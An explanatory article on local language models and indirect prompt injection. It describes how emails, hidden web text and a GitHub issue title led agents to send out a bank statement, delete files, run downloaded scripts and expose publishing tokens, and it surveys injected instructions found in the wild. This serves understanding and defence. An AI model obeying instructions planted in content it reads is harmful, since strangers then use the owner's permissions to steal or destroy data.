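# Running language models locally and the risk of injected instructions in AI agents

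## What a local model protects, and what an injected instruction is

A large language model is a program that continues a passage of text by computing which fragment probably comes next. A chat assistant combines this program with software that shows the continuation as a reply. Most users reach such models over the internet, and everything they type travels to a data centre where the model runs, which belongs to its developer or a cloud company. A local model runs on hardware that the user or the user's organisation controls. Open-weight models make this practical because anyone can download their trained parameters and run them. Well-known examples include the Qwen, DeepSeek and Llama families.

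Many people and organisations run models locally because they expect it to be safer. For a chat assistant, the main worry is who else can see the text. An agent is a language model in a loop with software that carries out the actions the model requests, such as reading a file, opening a web page or sending an email. Agents add another worry because some of what they read comes from strangers, who can put instructions into a web page as easily as information.

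### Four things that can be local

"Local" can mean that the model runs on the user's own hardware, that the agent program runs there, that the data is stored there, or that the system has no network connection. A product can have one of these properties without the others.

The computation and the agent program are especially easy to confuse. Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, opens files and runs commands on the developer's own machine, but the model runs elsewhere. According to the product's documentation page *Data usage*, the program "runs locally" and sends all user prompts and model outputs over the network. When the agent opens a source file to work on it, the contents go into the prompt and leave the laptop. Anthropic's *How Claude Science works with your data* describes the same division for a research product, which the customer installs and runs on its own computers while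 Anthropic supplies the model.

Other agents let the owner choose between a local and a hosted model. OpenClaw is an agent that people install on their own machines, and its *Local models* gives settings for a hosted model, a local one, or a mixture. One mixture uses the local model first and falls back to a hosted model "when the local box is down". The agent then runs on the local model most of the time, and its owner may not notice when it switches to the hosted one.

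Claude Code stores unencrypted transcripts of its sessions on the user's disk for 30 days by default, and Anthropic also keeps a copy for 30 days under its standard commercial terms. A private deployment, meaning a model run for only one organisation, may be on the organisation's premises or in a cloud account it controls, so the model may run on rented machines in another city.

An agent that uses a local model may also still send data over the network. Before Claude Code fetches a web page, it sends the site's hostname to Anthropic to check against a blocklist, whichever company supplies the model, unless the user turns the check off. Only a disconnected deployment, in which the model and its surrounding software have no outside connection, removes all such traffic. Engineers call such a system air-gapped when the separation is physical.

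### What the owner gains

The case for local models is strongest on retention. A hosted provider usually stores the prompts it receives for a while. Anthropic stores them for five years if an individual subscriber lets it train on their data. Business customers can negotiate for no retention, but such agreements have exceptions. *AI Privacy*, the policy of the code editor company Zed, excludes certain models because the provider insists on keeping data for safety reasons. All these customers depend on the provider's terms and security. *Local models do not stop data exfiltration*, by the security company PromptArmor, points out that no third party has to process the interactions when a customer runs a model on its own premises. A breach at the provider or a retention clause then no longer matters.

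Some organisations must also keep data within a country or region, and running a model on hardware in their own building can satisfy that requirement. OpenClaw treats hosted models with servers pinned to one region as a middle ground and local-only operation as "the strongest privacy path".

The owner also decides when the model changes. A provider can update or retire a hosted model on its own schedule, whereas downloaded parameters are a file, and the file will be the same next year. An organisation that has spent months testing a model can go on using exactly the model it tested. (This cuts both ways, since a fixed model keeps its weaknesses too.)

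Finally, the owner can cut the network entirely, which no customer of a hosted model can do. NVIDIA, which sells the hardware, claims that when OpenClaw runs with a local model, no data leaves the machine "unless you add cloud or external integrations". That condition matters because the first use NVIDIA suggests is a personal secretary with access to the owner's inbox and calendar, and anyone can send text to an inbox.

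### What the owner takes on

Anyone who hosts a model takes on work that a provider would otherwise do. The UK government's *Code of practice for the cyber security of AI* assigns security duties by role in the supply chain and allows for one organisation holding several roles, as a self-hoster does.

The Illinois ARDC, which regulates lawyers in the state, says a law firm running a local model must use a hardened environment, control who has access, segment its network, protect the trained parameters, and check that the model's files are genuine. Checking the files guards against malicious models, which the ARDC says people have already downloaded from widely used distribution sites. PromptArmor adds that the model's owner also becomes responsible for handling attacks that overload the model or increase its resource use.

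The UK Department for Business and Trade, in *Using self-hosted large language models (LLMs) securely in government* (2025), names cost as one of the biggest challenges of self-hosting. The department shares its graphics processors (the chips that run the models) among several teams, monitors usage, and experiments with fitting larger models onto smaller machines. For one user to run an agent comfortably, OpenClaw suggests two fully equipped Mac Studio computers or an equivalent rig, at about $30,000 or more. Cheaper hardware means smaller or more heavily compressed models, which OpenClaw warns raise the risk from injected instructions. It adds that local models lack the filters that hosted providers run.

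Some owners of local models fail to keep strangers out. SentinelLABS's *Silent Brothers* describes a scan, run with the internet-mapping company Censys, for publicly reachable copies of Ollama, a popular program for running local models. According to SC Media's *Internet-exposed Ollama AI servers widespread*, the scan found 175,000 servers, 48% of them with tool calling, which lets a model request actions. The models ran locally, but anyone on the internet could reach them.

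### One turn of the agent loop

The other half of the subject begins with how text gets into the model. Suppose that a worker asks an agent to summarise the newest complaint in a support queue. The software around the model, its harness, then goes through roughly these steps:

1. The harness collects the system prompt (the operator's standing instructions), descriptions of the available tools, the conversation so far and the worker's request. At this point they are separate messages, each with a label for its role.
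2. A chat template joins the messages into a single text, with special markers where one role ends and the next begins. Another component cuts the text into tokens, which are words or pieces of words, each with a number.
3. The model computes a probability for every possible next token. The program picks one, appends it, and repeats until the output is complete. Here the output is a tool call, a structured request to read the newest complaint.
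4. The harness recognises the tool call, checks whether its settings permit it, and fetches the complaint.
5. The harness adds the complaint to the list of messages and returns to the second step. The model now processes the worker's request and the stranger's complaint together.

A local model is one for which the third step happens on the owner's hardware. What the model computes there is the quantity

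P(xₙ₊₁ | x₁, x₂, …, xₙ),

the probability of the next token given all the tokens before it. The system prompt, the request and the complaint all sit somewhere among x₁ to xₙ, and the function has no separate input for who wrote what. The description in *Agentic AI and Security* (2025) is of one growing document: the user adds some text, the model adds some, and a tool adds the text that it has fetched.

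Role markers indicate who wrote each piece of text, and developers train models to give some roles more weight than others. But the markers are tokens too, so they are only evidence of authorship, and an attacker can try to fake them. According to OpenClaw's *Prompt injection*, some self-hosted servers convert a string that looks like a role marker into the real marker, so a fetched web page could fake the start of a message from the operator. OpenClaw deletes such strings from outside material before the model receives it. The large hosted providers do their own cleaning, but the owner of a local model is responsible for it.

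### Direct and indirect injection

The software developer Simon Willison named the problem in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* (2022). A day earlier, Riley Goodside had posted experiments with GPT-3, an early OpenAI model. Goodside told the model to translate a passage into French, but the passage contained an instruction to ignore the task and print a taunt. GPT-3 printed the taunt, and did so again after Goodside rewrote the prompt to warn that the passage might contain tricks. Willison saw this as a security flaw because developers were already building products by joining their own instructions to whatever a user typed.

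This is direct injection, where the attacker types into the application. The attacker's potential gain depends on what the application can do, which in 2022 was often very little. Willison (2023), in *Prompt injection*, conceded that tricking a translation service into talking like a pirate does little harm. He argued that the risk grew once developers gave models tools. An assistant that can read, send and delete a person's email might obey an order that arrives in one of those emails.

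In that example the attacker never interacts directly with the assistant. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, introduced the term indirect prompt injection for attacks in which someone places instructions in content that a model will later read on another person's behalf. They demonstrated it on Bing Chat, Microsoft's GPT-4 assistant, which could read the page open in the user's browser. Text on the page affected the model even when it was invisible to a human visitor. The user only had to open one such page and ask a question for the assistant to coax out their name in conversation and offer a link that would send it to the attacker.

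Greshake and colleagues also classified the ways an attacker can deliver injected instructions. An attacker can publish the text and wait for a search to retrieve it, send it by email, or get users to paste it in. A short first instruction can tell the model to fetch a longer one, and images can also contain the text. The effects they considered include data theft, fraud, and worms, in which an email assistant forwards the injected text to the next victim. They noted in 2023 that even an offline model that searches someone's personal files or documentation can receive injected instructions if an attacker has poisoned those files.

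People often confuse prompt injection with jailbreaking, in which users persuade a model to break its developer's rules. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, objects to this because developers who confuse the two tend to see injection as an embarrassment for the model's vendor rather than a problem of their own. In a jailbreak the instructions come from the user, whereas in an indirect injection they come from an outsider, conflict with the user's, and could be carried out with the user's permissions.

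### The confused deputy and the lethal trifecta

Computer security had a name for this kind of borrowed authority, the "confused deputy", decades before language models. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) tells the "nearly true story" of a compiler (a program that translates source code) at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The compiler had permission to write in its own directory because it kept usage statistics there, and the company's billing records were in the same directory. Users could tell the compiler where to put its debugging output, and one user gave the name of the billing file. The operating system let the compiler overwrite the bills because the compiler had permission to write there.

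The user had no permission to write to the billing file, but the compiler did, and it used that permission on the user's behalf. Hardy attributed the problem to the compiler having authority from two sources and no way to indicate which one it was using. Tymshare first added a way for it to "switch hats" between the two, but some programs turned out to need more than two hats. Hardy preferred to use capabilities, which are references that both identify a file and grant permission to use it. Under that scheme, users pass the compiler a capability for their output file, and they can't pass one for the billing file because they don't have one.

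An agent that reads a poisoned complaint is in the same position as Hardy's compiler. The stranger who wrote the complaint cannot open the company's files, but the agent can, and the harness receives only a valid request from it. The agent's case is harder because the compiler received the file name through a known slot, so a programmer could point to the part of the request that came from the user. A tool call comes out of the whole sequence of tokens, and no record shows which of them prompted it. In *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents*, Chu (2026) reviewed 116 papers and traced every attack on the tool-using part of agents to a single cause, misplaced trust in who is speaking. No second reader checked Chu's classification of the papers, though the finding agrees with the mechanism described here.

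Willison attributes the risk of data theft to a combination of three things, which he calls the lethal trifecta: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. An agent with all three can read a secret, receive an instruction to send it, and send it. *Agentic AI and Security* describes an example involving Jira, a program for tracking work. A company had set Jira to import support tickets from the public. An attacker filed a ticket asking the agent to look for strings that began like a login token and post any it found as a comment, which the public could read.

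The outbound channel in that case was a comment box, which few people would think of as a network connection. An image can also serve as a channel, because the program that displays it must request it from a server, and the requested address can contain stolen text. According to Willison, vendors have mostly responded to reported attacks by closing the channel the attacker used. That stops the theft, but the model remains just as likely to follow the injected instruction. The trifecta also covers only theft, and an agent with permission to delete files can do damage without an outbound channel.

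### Why a complete fix may never come

Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack on databases. SQL is the language programs use to query databases. If a website builds a query by pasting in whatever a visitor typed, the visitor can type a fragment of SQL and the database will execute it. Parameterised queries fixed this by having the program send the query with blanks in it and supply the visitor's text separately, so that the database never interprets that text as a command. In 2022 Willison hoped for a similar fix for language models, with separate inputs for instructions and data. By April 2023 he thought this would be extremely difficult, perhaps impossible, with the models' current architecture.

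In December 2025, the UK's National Cyber Security Centre warned against comparing prompt injection to SQL injection. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a post by David C, the centre's technical director for platforms research, argues that SQL injection can be fixed because a database treats commands and data differently, so engineers can enforce the difference. A language model has no such difference to enforce. In his words, "there is only ever 'next token'". Detecting attacks, training models to put instructions ahead of data, and marking the data for the model are all attempts to add a distinction to a technology that lacks one. He concludes that prompt injection may never be fully mitigated in the way that SQL injection can be, and he calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy", unlike the classical confused deputy, which engineers can repair.

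This argument is based on how current models work, and David C hedges it accordingly. It does not imply that every model is equally easy to fool. OpenClaw considers the best recent models substantially more resistant than older ones and recommends them as a first layer of defence. But greater resistance lowers the success rate of attacks, and an attacker can often try again. Willison says that 95% is a failing grade in web security for a filter meant to catch attacks. If attempts were independent, an attacker who tried 20 times against such a filter would have a 64% chance of getting through at least once (1 − 0.95²⁰). Real attackers do better because they learn from their failures.

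David C therefore wants designers to assume that some injections will succeed and to limit their effects by constraining the model's actions with ordinary software outside it. He likes a rule from an online discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista that a model processing a party's text keeps only that party's privileges. An agent reading email from random outsiders would then have only the tools one would give a random outsider. The rule is simple, but it would prevent much of what people want agents to do. Where a system cannot tolerate the remaining risk, he suggests that a language model may be the wrong tool.

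Running a model on your own hardware raises two questions. The first is which dangers this removes and which it leaves unchanged. The second is how, when an agent with permission to act reads untrusted content, the person who wrote that content can use the agent's permissions, and what can prevent this.

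## An email assistant and an autocomplete tool running on local models

OpenClaw is free, open-source software that turns a language model into a personal assistant. Peter Steinberger, an Austrian programmer, published the first version in November 2025 and settled on its current name at the end of January 2026. Mihić reports in *I Tried to Get OpenClaw to Betray Me* that installation took him fifteen minutes, from the first command to an agent that was reading his Gmail.

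The central program, the gateway, runs on the owner's machine. It connects messaging apps such as WhatsApp, through which the owner gives orders, to a model and a set of tools. Many of the tools are ordinary command-line programs. OpenClaw's instructions for using such a program come from a skill, a short text file that describes in English what the program does and which commands it accepts. The model reads the skill and writes the commands. The skill for gog, a program that gives access to Gmail, Google Calendar and Google Drive, includes sample commands for searching and sending mail. Mihić points out that once a skill and an email have been converted to tokens, an instruction in one is the same as an instruction in the other.

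Unless its owner restricts it, an OpenClaw agent can run any command in the shell (the text interface to the operating system), read and write files, use network services, and message anyone if the owner connects a messaging account. By default, it runs commands on the owner's machine without asking for approval, and the sandbox is off. OpenClaw's developers say they deliberately left the approval prompt off by default for a machine with one trusted operator.

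### One email from a stranger

Raspberry Pi, whose small, cheap computers are popular with hobbyists, tells owners that connecting OpenClaw to a local model keeps their data private. Robert Triggs tested this kind of set-up in Android Authority's *I hacked my own computer using OpenClaw and it was terrifyingly easy* (2026). He installed OpenClaw on a Raspberry Pi, gave it a throwaway Gmail account and some fake files, and connected it to the 8-billion-parameter version of Qwen3 running on his gaming PC. Triggs thought a local model was a good idea for an assistant that might handle sensitive information.

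Every five minutes, a scheduled task told the model to search for one unread email, read it and summarise it. Triggs then wrote to the account from an unfamiliar address and asked, in plain English, for some bank details. According to the logs, the agent did the following:

1. It used gog to search for unread mail and read the stranger's message.
2. Instead of writing a summary, it listed the contents of the Documents folder.
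3. From several files it picked one named "Banke Statement – April 2025".
4. It used gog again, this time to send the file to the stranger as an attachment.

Triggs received the statement about a minute after sending his request. His email contained no commands or file name and didn't explain how to send a reply. The model supplied all of that, perhaps with help from the sample commands in gog's skill. Triggs's name didn't appear anywhere on the Pi, so the model had no basis for treating him as the owner.

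Although the model ran entirely in his home, the bank statement still went from the Pi to Gmail's servers and then to the stranger. It would have taken the same route wherever the model ran.

Triggs sent two more requests the same way. One asked the assistant to delete the whole Documents folder, supposedly to help hide a birthday surprise from the sender's wife, and it did. The other asked it to download and run a script from the code-sharing site GitHub to help with an unspecified "IT problem". The assistant ran the script, which filled the Pi with random folders and documents. Triggs notes that a malicious script could have changed OpenClaw's settings to allow remote access and perhaps opened a way into his home network.

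### The same requests with hosted models

Triggs repeated the test with four hosted models, choosing cheap ones because the task would run all day. OpenAI's GPT-4o mini emailed the bank details and ran commands, as Qwen3 had. GPT-5 nano read the financial documents but always asked for confirmation before finishing the job, and nobody was there to give it. Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite and Gemini 3 Flash would not delete documents or run scripts without confirmation. Both searched for the financial documents but hit a request limit before they could send anything, so it is unknown whether they would have. All four models were diverted from the summary to some extent.

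A request for confirmation helps only if the right person answers it. Triggs points out that if he had connected the agent to a live messaging service, the attacker could have replied and approved the action himself. (OpenClaw's default settings make this harder, since the agent ignores direct messages from unknown senders until the owner approves them.)

Running the agent on Qwen3, a local model, gave the owner the privacy from AI companies that he wanted, but the stranger who sent the email still received the bank statement. When the agent used GPT-5 nano, the stranger received nothing, but OpenAI received the financial documents because the agent had to send them to the model for it to read them.

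Triggs's test is thin evidence of how often such attacks succeed. He ran it alone, reports no success rates, and used fake files and only small or cheap models. He also fetched the mail with a command rather than through OpenClaw's own Gmail integration, which labels incoming messages as outside content, so the test may have skipped one layer of defence. It does show that a single ordinary-looking email can be enough for an attack to succeed. In a separate demonstration described in Kaspersky's *Don't get pinched*, Matvey Kukuy, chief executive of Archestra.AI, used an email to extract a private key from a computer running OpenClaw.

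Mihić's own trial went differently. He sent himself a fake delivery confirmation with a hidden request to forward any email containing words related to password managers. The leading hosted model he was using flagged the sender, pointed out the hidden text and refused. He then removed the giveaways one at a time, making the text visible, inventing a more plausible sender and asking for a standing workflow instead of an immediate theft. The model caught every version. Cheaper models were less reliable, though Mihić gives no counts. It took a public competition to measure such differences properly.

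Mihić concludes that an OpenClaw owner's security depends almost entirely on which model is connected that day. OpenClaw's suggested fallback settings can switch from a hosted model to a local one when the provider is overloaded, so a weaker model may read the inbox.

### What the sender gained

Before the agent read his email, the stranger could put text in an inbox, and that was all. Afterwards he had the use of the agent's permissions:

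| | Before the agent reads the email | After the agent follows it |
|---|---|---|
| Documents on the Pi | The sender cannot see them | He can have the agent find, send and delete them |
| The Gmail account | He can write to it | He can have the agent send mail from it, and could ask for the owner's other messages (not tried) |
| Google Drive | He has no access | He could have the agent search it (not tried) |
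| Programs on the Pi | He cannot run any | He can have the agent download and run a script |
| The home network | He is outside it | He could use a script to look for other machines (not tried) |

This is the confused deputy from Hardy's story of the compiler, with a much more versatile deputy. One could call what the stranger acquires his inherited reach. Let S be the set of things he can do on his own and A the set of things the agent can do. If the agent follows his instructions, he can bring about anything in

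S ∪ A,

meaning everything in either set. Suppose the agent follows them with probability p. A more resistant model lowers p and leaves A as it was. Moving the model from a data centre to a gaming PC also leaves A as it was, and may raise p if the owner has to use a smaller model to fit the hardware.

A lists what the software permits, but a weak model may fail to carry out a complicated instruction. Triggs expects a more powerful model to be better at searching deeply nested folders, so a stronger model that does follow an injected instruction may do more harm with the same permissions.

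### Removing one permission at a time

In Triggs's set-up, the agent did nearly everything through the shell. It listed the Documents folder with a shell command, and gog is a program that it runs from the command line, so turning off OpenClaw's separate file tools would have made no difference. To see what each permission contributes, suppose instead that the agent has three tools, one for reading and writing files, one for sending mail and one for running shell commands. It can also read the inbox, since that is its job.

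If file access is removed first, the shell must lose it too, for example by running in a sandbox that doesn't contain the documents. The stranger can then no longer obtain the bank statement or delete the folder. He can still ask for the contents of other emails, because Google's permission to read mail covers every message in the account, and for many people the inbox is more revealing than the Documents folder. He can also still run a script inside the sandbox and use whatever network access it has.

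If the agent keeps its files and its shell but cannot send mail, it can't email the attachment. Google makes this possible by separating permission to read mail from permission to send it. However, a script run from the shell can still upload the statement to a website. The attack that deletes the folder also still works, because it doesn't require sending anything out.

Removing the shell helps more than removing either of the other tools, because a script can do whatever the agent's account on the machine can do. Without the shell, the stranger can no longer use the downloaded program and probably has no route into the home network. He can still steal the bank statement, which takes only the file and mail tools, and he can delete the folder if the file tool allows deletion.

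With all three gone, the agent can read mail and write a summary. The stranger can still tamper with the summary, perhaps making it omit a message from the bank or present a fake invoice as genuine. No money would move unless the owner believed the summary and acted on it.

OpenClaw's developers recommend something close to this. Their restricted starting configuration turns off the shell and file tools, and they now advise giving untrusted mail to a separate reader agent, which has no tools and passes a summary to the main agent. Two defaults can undermine this arrangement. The Gmail integration gives each message its own conversation but leaves the agent's tool permissions in place, so the owner has to restrict those separately. OpenClaw's agents can also message one another unless the owner limits which pairs can communicate. Even after the owner changes both settings, the email's sender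 may have influenced the summary, so the main agent shouldn't treat it as if the owner had written it.

OpenClaw's developers do not count an attack like Triggs's as a vulnerability. They usually close reports that consist only of prompt injection, unless the reporter can show that the attack also got past a policy, a login check or a sandbox. There is some logic to this, since the agent had permission to send that file and no code failed. But owners who keep the default settings have never really decided to let a stranger's email lead to a shell command, and the developers could choose defaults that make them decide. One option is to require approval before each command, which would help only if owners read what they approve.

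The developers also advise against using small models for untrusted inboxes. Triggs had picked a small model because it fitted his PC and kept his data at home. Someone in his position has to rely mainly on restricting the assistant's permissions.

### An autocomplete tool and a browsing agent

In 2026, the web browser company Brave tested attacks on two products that differ in where the model runs and what the software is allowed to do. *Indirect Prompt Injection remains a fundamental security challenge for AI* covers both attacks.

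Cotypist is an autocomplete program for Macs that predicts the user's next words in any application, using a model that runs entirely on the machine. Brave's researchers placed instructions in a local document. When someone typed about the weather in London, Cotypist suggested the word "BANANA". The researchers also got it to suggest the user's credentials.

Cotypist can only suggest words, and the user has to press Tab to insert them. A wrong word is a nuisance, but someone who accepts suggestions out of habit could put a suggested password into an email without noticing. An attacker would still have to be able to read that email, so the theft would be far less direct than the one in Triggs's test.

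Mozilla, which makes the Firefox browser, runs Tabstack in the cloud. Developers send Tabstack a task, and its agent browses the web to carry it out. Brave's researchers asked it to summarise a page they controlled, which contained instructions in text invisible to human visitors. The agent opened a form on another site, filled in the user's message and the conversation so far, and submitted the form to a Brave server without asking for confirmation. It never summarised the page. The reasoning logs show that the model treated the hidden text as directions for producing the summary. Tabstack had an optional setting for describing limits on the agent's behaviour, but it was off by default.

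In both products, the model followed instructions in someone else's text. Brave's researchers conclude that running a model locally does not remove this flaw. If anything, they expect local models to be more at risk because such models are usually less powerful. They attribute the difference in damage between the two products to what each could do.

Two demonstrations on different products, with different models and different tasks, cannot show how much each of these factors matters. Brave also competes with Mozilla in the browser market, although Mozilla confirmed the Tabstack findings. The argument is stronger when Triggs's test is set beside Brave's, along with Riley Goodside's experiment of 2022, in which GPT-3 printed a taunt instead of a translation:

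| | The software can only produce text | The software can act |
|---|---|---|
| Local model | Cotypist suggests a wrong word or a password | OpenClaw with Qwen3 emails a bank statement, deletes a folder and runs a script |
| Hosted model | GPT-3 prints a taunt | Tabstack submits a conversation to an attacker's form |

Both products in the right-hand column did serious damage, one with a local model and one with a hosted model. The worst result in the left-hand column was a password that the user would still have had to accept. Triggs's agent ran on a local model and did more damage than Tabstack. Brave's pair alone could give the impression that local software is safer, because its local product happened to have few permissions.

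### How the vendors responded

Brave reported the Tabstack flaw on 13 May 2026. Mozilla confirmed it the next day and released a fix on 1 June, and Brave's researchers checked the fix. Mozilla's *Hardening AI Web Agents* explains that the engineers assumed the model would sometimes follow injected text, and focused on preventing it from sending data out when it did.

Their main change was to put checks, written as ordinary software, between the agent's decisions and the browser. The checks don't try to recognise malicious wording. They are based on what kind of field the agent wants to fill, where the value came from and whether a person approved it. The agent may still use search boxes, date pickers and similar controls, but it may not fill free-text or sensitive fields on its own, or submit a form containing data it entered without approval. An attacker could disguise a data-collecting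 field as a search box, so even permitted submissions can go only to the site the agent is already on. When the software blocks an action, it may show the user how to allow it, but it keeps that explanation out of the model's input. Otherwise a malicious page could instruct the agent to persuade the user to turn the protection off.

Some customers need an agent that fills in forms on other companies' sites. They can supply a list of trusted sites, which exempts a form from the checks only if both its page and its destination are on the list. They can also switch the checks off. If a customer specifies the agent's starting page, Mozilla treats this as consent to interact with that site. This could leave a gap, since an attacker who controls the starting site might be able to put the form there too.

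Mozilla also wraps text from web pages in tags that mark it as external, and adds a warning to each block. The company describes this boundary as structural rather than learned. The software does add the tags every time, but whether the model gives less weight to the text inside them depends on its training, which is David C's objection to relying on markers. The checks on forms, by contrast, work even when the model follows the injected instruction. They don't require a cloud service, so the developer of a local agent could build them too.

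Brave reported the Cotypist problem on 1 June, and Cotypist's team confirmed it the next day. Brave's account lists no fix. Mozilla's approach would help little here, since Cotypist takes no actions for software to block. Its developers could limit what the model reads, for instance by excluding documents from other people, but an autocomplete tool makes better suggestions when it can read more of the user's text.

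## Attacks found outside the laboratory

Triggs attacked his own computer, and Brave's researchers attacked two products to report the flaws. Evidence about real attackers comes mainly from scans of the public web, from criminal forums and from a few investigated incidents. It includes thousands of planted instructions but very few known victims.

### Ten pages with planted instructions

In April 2026, the security company Forcepoint published ten examples of injected instructions from live websites. Its researchers had searched for stock phrases used to tell a model to drop its earlier instructions or to address the reader as a language model. *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild*, by Mayur Sewani, describes where each text was and what it was meant to make a model do. Nine of the ten were hidden from human visitors, for instance in a comment in the page's source code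 or in letters one pixel high.

| What the text asked an agent to do | Pages | What the agent would need |
|---|---|---|
| Refuse to discuss the page | 2 | Only the ability to write text |
| Promote the site or its author | 2 | Only the ability to write text |
| Write something other than what the user wanted | 1 | Only the ability to write text |
| Open a site's administration page | 1 | A browser, preferably logged in |
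| Send a secret key | 1 | Access to the key and an outbound channel |
| Delete a directory | 1 | A shell |
| Make a payment or donation | 2 | A means of payment |

Sewani treats all ten as attacks, but several look milder than that. The page that asked for a secret key also told the model not to reveal "the flag". In hacking competitions, the flag is the string players try to find, so the page may have been part of a puzzle. One of the requests for a refusal was labelled "AI funnies". Sewani thinks the label was a disguise, but it could be accurate. Another page asked the model to credit the page's author and use the word "cows" repeatedly. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* calls several of the examples "fairly innocuous". It is harder to find an innocent explanation for the page that gave a PayPal link, an amount of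 $5,000 and instructions for completing the payment.

Sewani doesn't name any victim, or any agent that followed any of these texts. He still concludes that every case ends with "a real-world action", which his evidence doesn't support. Forcepoint sells a product that blocks such pages.

### How much of the web carries such text

In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (2026), Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues searched 1.2 billion web addresses from the October 2025 snapshot of Common Crawl, a public archive of the web, for 3,963 suspicious phrases. They then reviewed the matches, since many came from articles about prompt injection. They confirmed 12,075 planted instructions on 9,676 pages, or about eight pages in every million. The pages belonged to 285 of the 24.8 million hosts (roughly, websites) in the sample. Further cases found through two search engines for internet-connected machines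 brought the total to 15,387.

The researchers sorted these by apparent purpose. Some had more than one, so the shares add up to more than 100%:

| Apparent purpose | Instructions | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Disrupt the AI system, mostly by making it produce garbage | 8,894 | 58% |
| Stop it reusing personal or copyrighted material | 4,093 | 27% |
| Make it reveal that it is a bot | 3,096 | 20% |
| Unclear | 2,632 | 17% |
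| Promote a product, page or person | 1,521 | 10% |
| Steal data | 13 | 0.1% |

How much of this is malicious depends on the definition. Khodayari and colleagues class disruption, promotion and theft as offensive. But much of the disruption targets programs that copy websites in bulk, and a site owner who feeds such a program random numbers is hardly malicious. The disruption category also includes 157 attempts to inject commands, such as orders to delete files or databases. Together with the 13 attempts at data theft, these make up about 1% of the total.

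In the Common Crawl sample, site operators had planted 81% of the instructions on their own sites. Only 220, under 2%, came from users writing in places such as comment sections, where a stranger can reach the readers of someone else's site. Of the pages with an archived copy from a year earlier, two-thirds already contained an instruction then. More than half of the instructions in the full collection were in HTTP headers, the technical information a server sends ahead of a page, so an agent that gives its model only the page's text would never pass them on. When Khodayari and colleagues fed planted instructions to 13 models in a summarising test, the models seldom followed them.

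Templates shared between sites could come from "organized tooling", as Sewani suggests, or from people copying a trick they have seen elsewhere. The larger sample had just as much reuse, with 54 templates covering 95% of cases, yet most of those texts came from site operators with no obvious criminal aim.

Google scanned several monthly editions of Common Crawl, each with two to three billion pages. Its researchers searched for known phrases, had the Gemini model classify the results, and checked those by hand. Most of the injected instructions they found were pranks, advice to summarisers, self-promotion or attempts to keep AI agents away. The few attempts at theft or destruction were crude, and many looked like experiments. The malicious category grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google gives no counts, so the increase could be a handful of pages. Help Net Security's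 *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* (2026) compares Google's report with Forcepoint's and notes that neither team found a sophisticated, coordinated campaign.

Some pages look like the work of criminals. *Fooling AI Agents*, from Palo Alto Networks' research group Unit 42, describes a scam advertisement for "military glasses". Its page contained 24 attempts to make an automated ad reviewer approve it, hidden in different ways in case a filter caught some of them. Unit 42 knows of no deployed reviewer that was fooled by such an attack. The security company Zscaler found a site offering a fake programming library, with hidden instructions for an agent to pay a "license fee" of a few dollars in cryptocurrency. According to SC Media's *Malicious websites trick AI agents into crypto payments, context poisoning*, the attacker's wallet had received some payments, but none for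 the requested amount. When Zscaler tested 26 models in a sandbox, four paid, including two open-weight Llama models, so an agent with a wallet could plausibly be fooled too.

These scans probably undercount attacks. Searching for known phrases misses unusual wording, disguised text and most other languages. A malicious site can also show its instructions only to visitors it recognises as AI agents and serve Common Crawl a clean page. And no scan of the public web covers private email, the channel Triggs used.

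### Tools for sale

Criminals on closed forums are also developing, refining and advertising tools for indirect injection, according to *Notes from Underground* by Proofpoint, a security company that monitors the forums. Some advertised methods put the instructions in calendar invitations or malicious online advertisements. Subscriptions start at about $150 a month, according to Tarre (2026) in *Proofpoint flags underground AI prompt injection tools*.

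Help Net Security's *Stolen AI API keys are paying for hackers' autonomous scans* (2026) reports results from the security company Bitsight, which followed 16 forums from February to August 2026. Mentions of AI agents, indirect injection and the Model Context Protocol (a standard way of connecting agents to tools) rose by 67%. This figure combines three topics, so interest in injection alone may have grown much more or much less. Bitsight also found a seller who offered an autonomous hacking tool and claimed 1,072 findings on 199 machines, a figure it could not verify. The advertisement shows that the seller expects buyers, but it is not evidence that the tool works, because sellers on these forums have every reason to exaggerate.

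There is better evidence of criminals tampering with skills, the add-ons that people install in their agents. The security company ESET examined 900,000 skills in public repositories. Infosecurity Magazine's *Cybercriminals Plant Malicious AI Agents in Open Source Tool Repositories* (2026) reports that the number ESET blocked as malicious rose from about 600 to over 3,000 in the first half of 2026. Some of the blocked skills steal data or override the user's instructions. Unlike a web page, a skill is something the owner chooses to install, but a local model offers no protection from either.

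### From an issue title to a software release

The best-documented case of real harm began with Cline, an open-source programming agent. Its developers work in public on GitHub, a code-sharing site where anyone with an account can report a problem by opening an "issue". On 21 December 2025, they added an automated job in which Claude, Anthropic's model, read and responded to each new issue, with access to a shell for running commands.

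The security researcher Adnan Khan noticed the danger. Khan (2026), in *Clinejection*, explains how an issue could lead to control of Cline's releases:

1. The attacker opens an issue with an instruction in its title. The job puts the title directly into the model's prompt.
2. The agent obeys and installs a software package that the attacker controls. The package runs a script as soon as it is installed, so the model has no chance to inspect it.
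3. The script can't change Cline's code, but it can write to a cache, a store of files that GitHub's automated jobs keep for reuse. It fills the cache with junk until GitHub discards the older files, then puts altered ones in their place.
4. That night, another job loads the altered files while preparing a test release. This job holds the tokens (secret keys) for publishing Cline, and the attacker's code can now steal them.
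5. The token for test releases on npm, a public registry of JavaScript software, also works for ordinary releases. With it, the attacker can publish a new version to every user.

The agent's access token only let it read the code and edit issues. In the terms used for Triggs's email, though, the set A also included writing to a cache that the more powerful nightly job trusted. That job was in effect a second confused deputy, even though it contained no language model. Assessing an agent's risk therefore requires checking which other programs use what the agent can change, as well as listing its own permissions.

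Khan reported the flaw privately on 1 January 2026 and got no useful reply. He published it on 9 February, and Cline's developers removed the job within half an hour. They also began replacing their publishing tokens, but deleted the wrong npm token and left the exposed one active. The management page they checked showed no active tokens. A day later, an anonymous correspondent told Khan that stolen credentials still worked. Khan passed this on, and the developers assured him they had replaced everything. On 17 February, someone used the remaining token to publish an altered version of Cline's command-line program.

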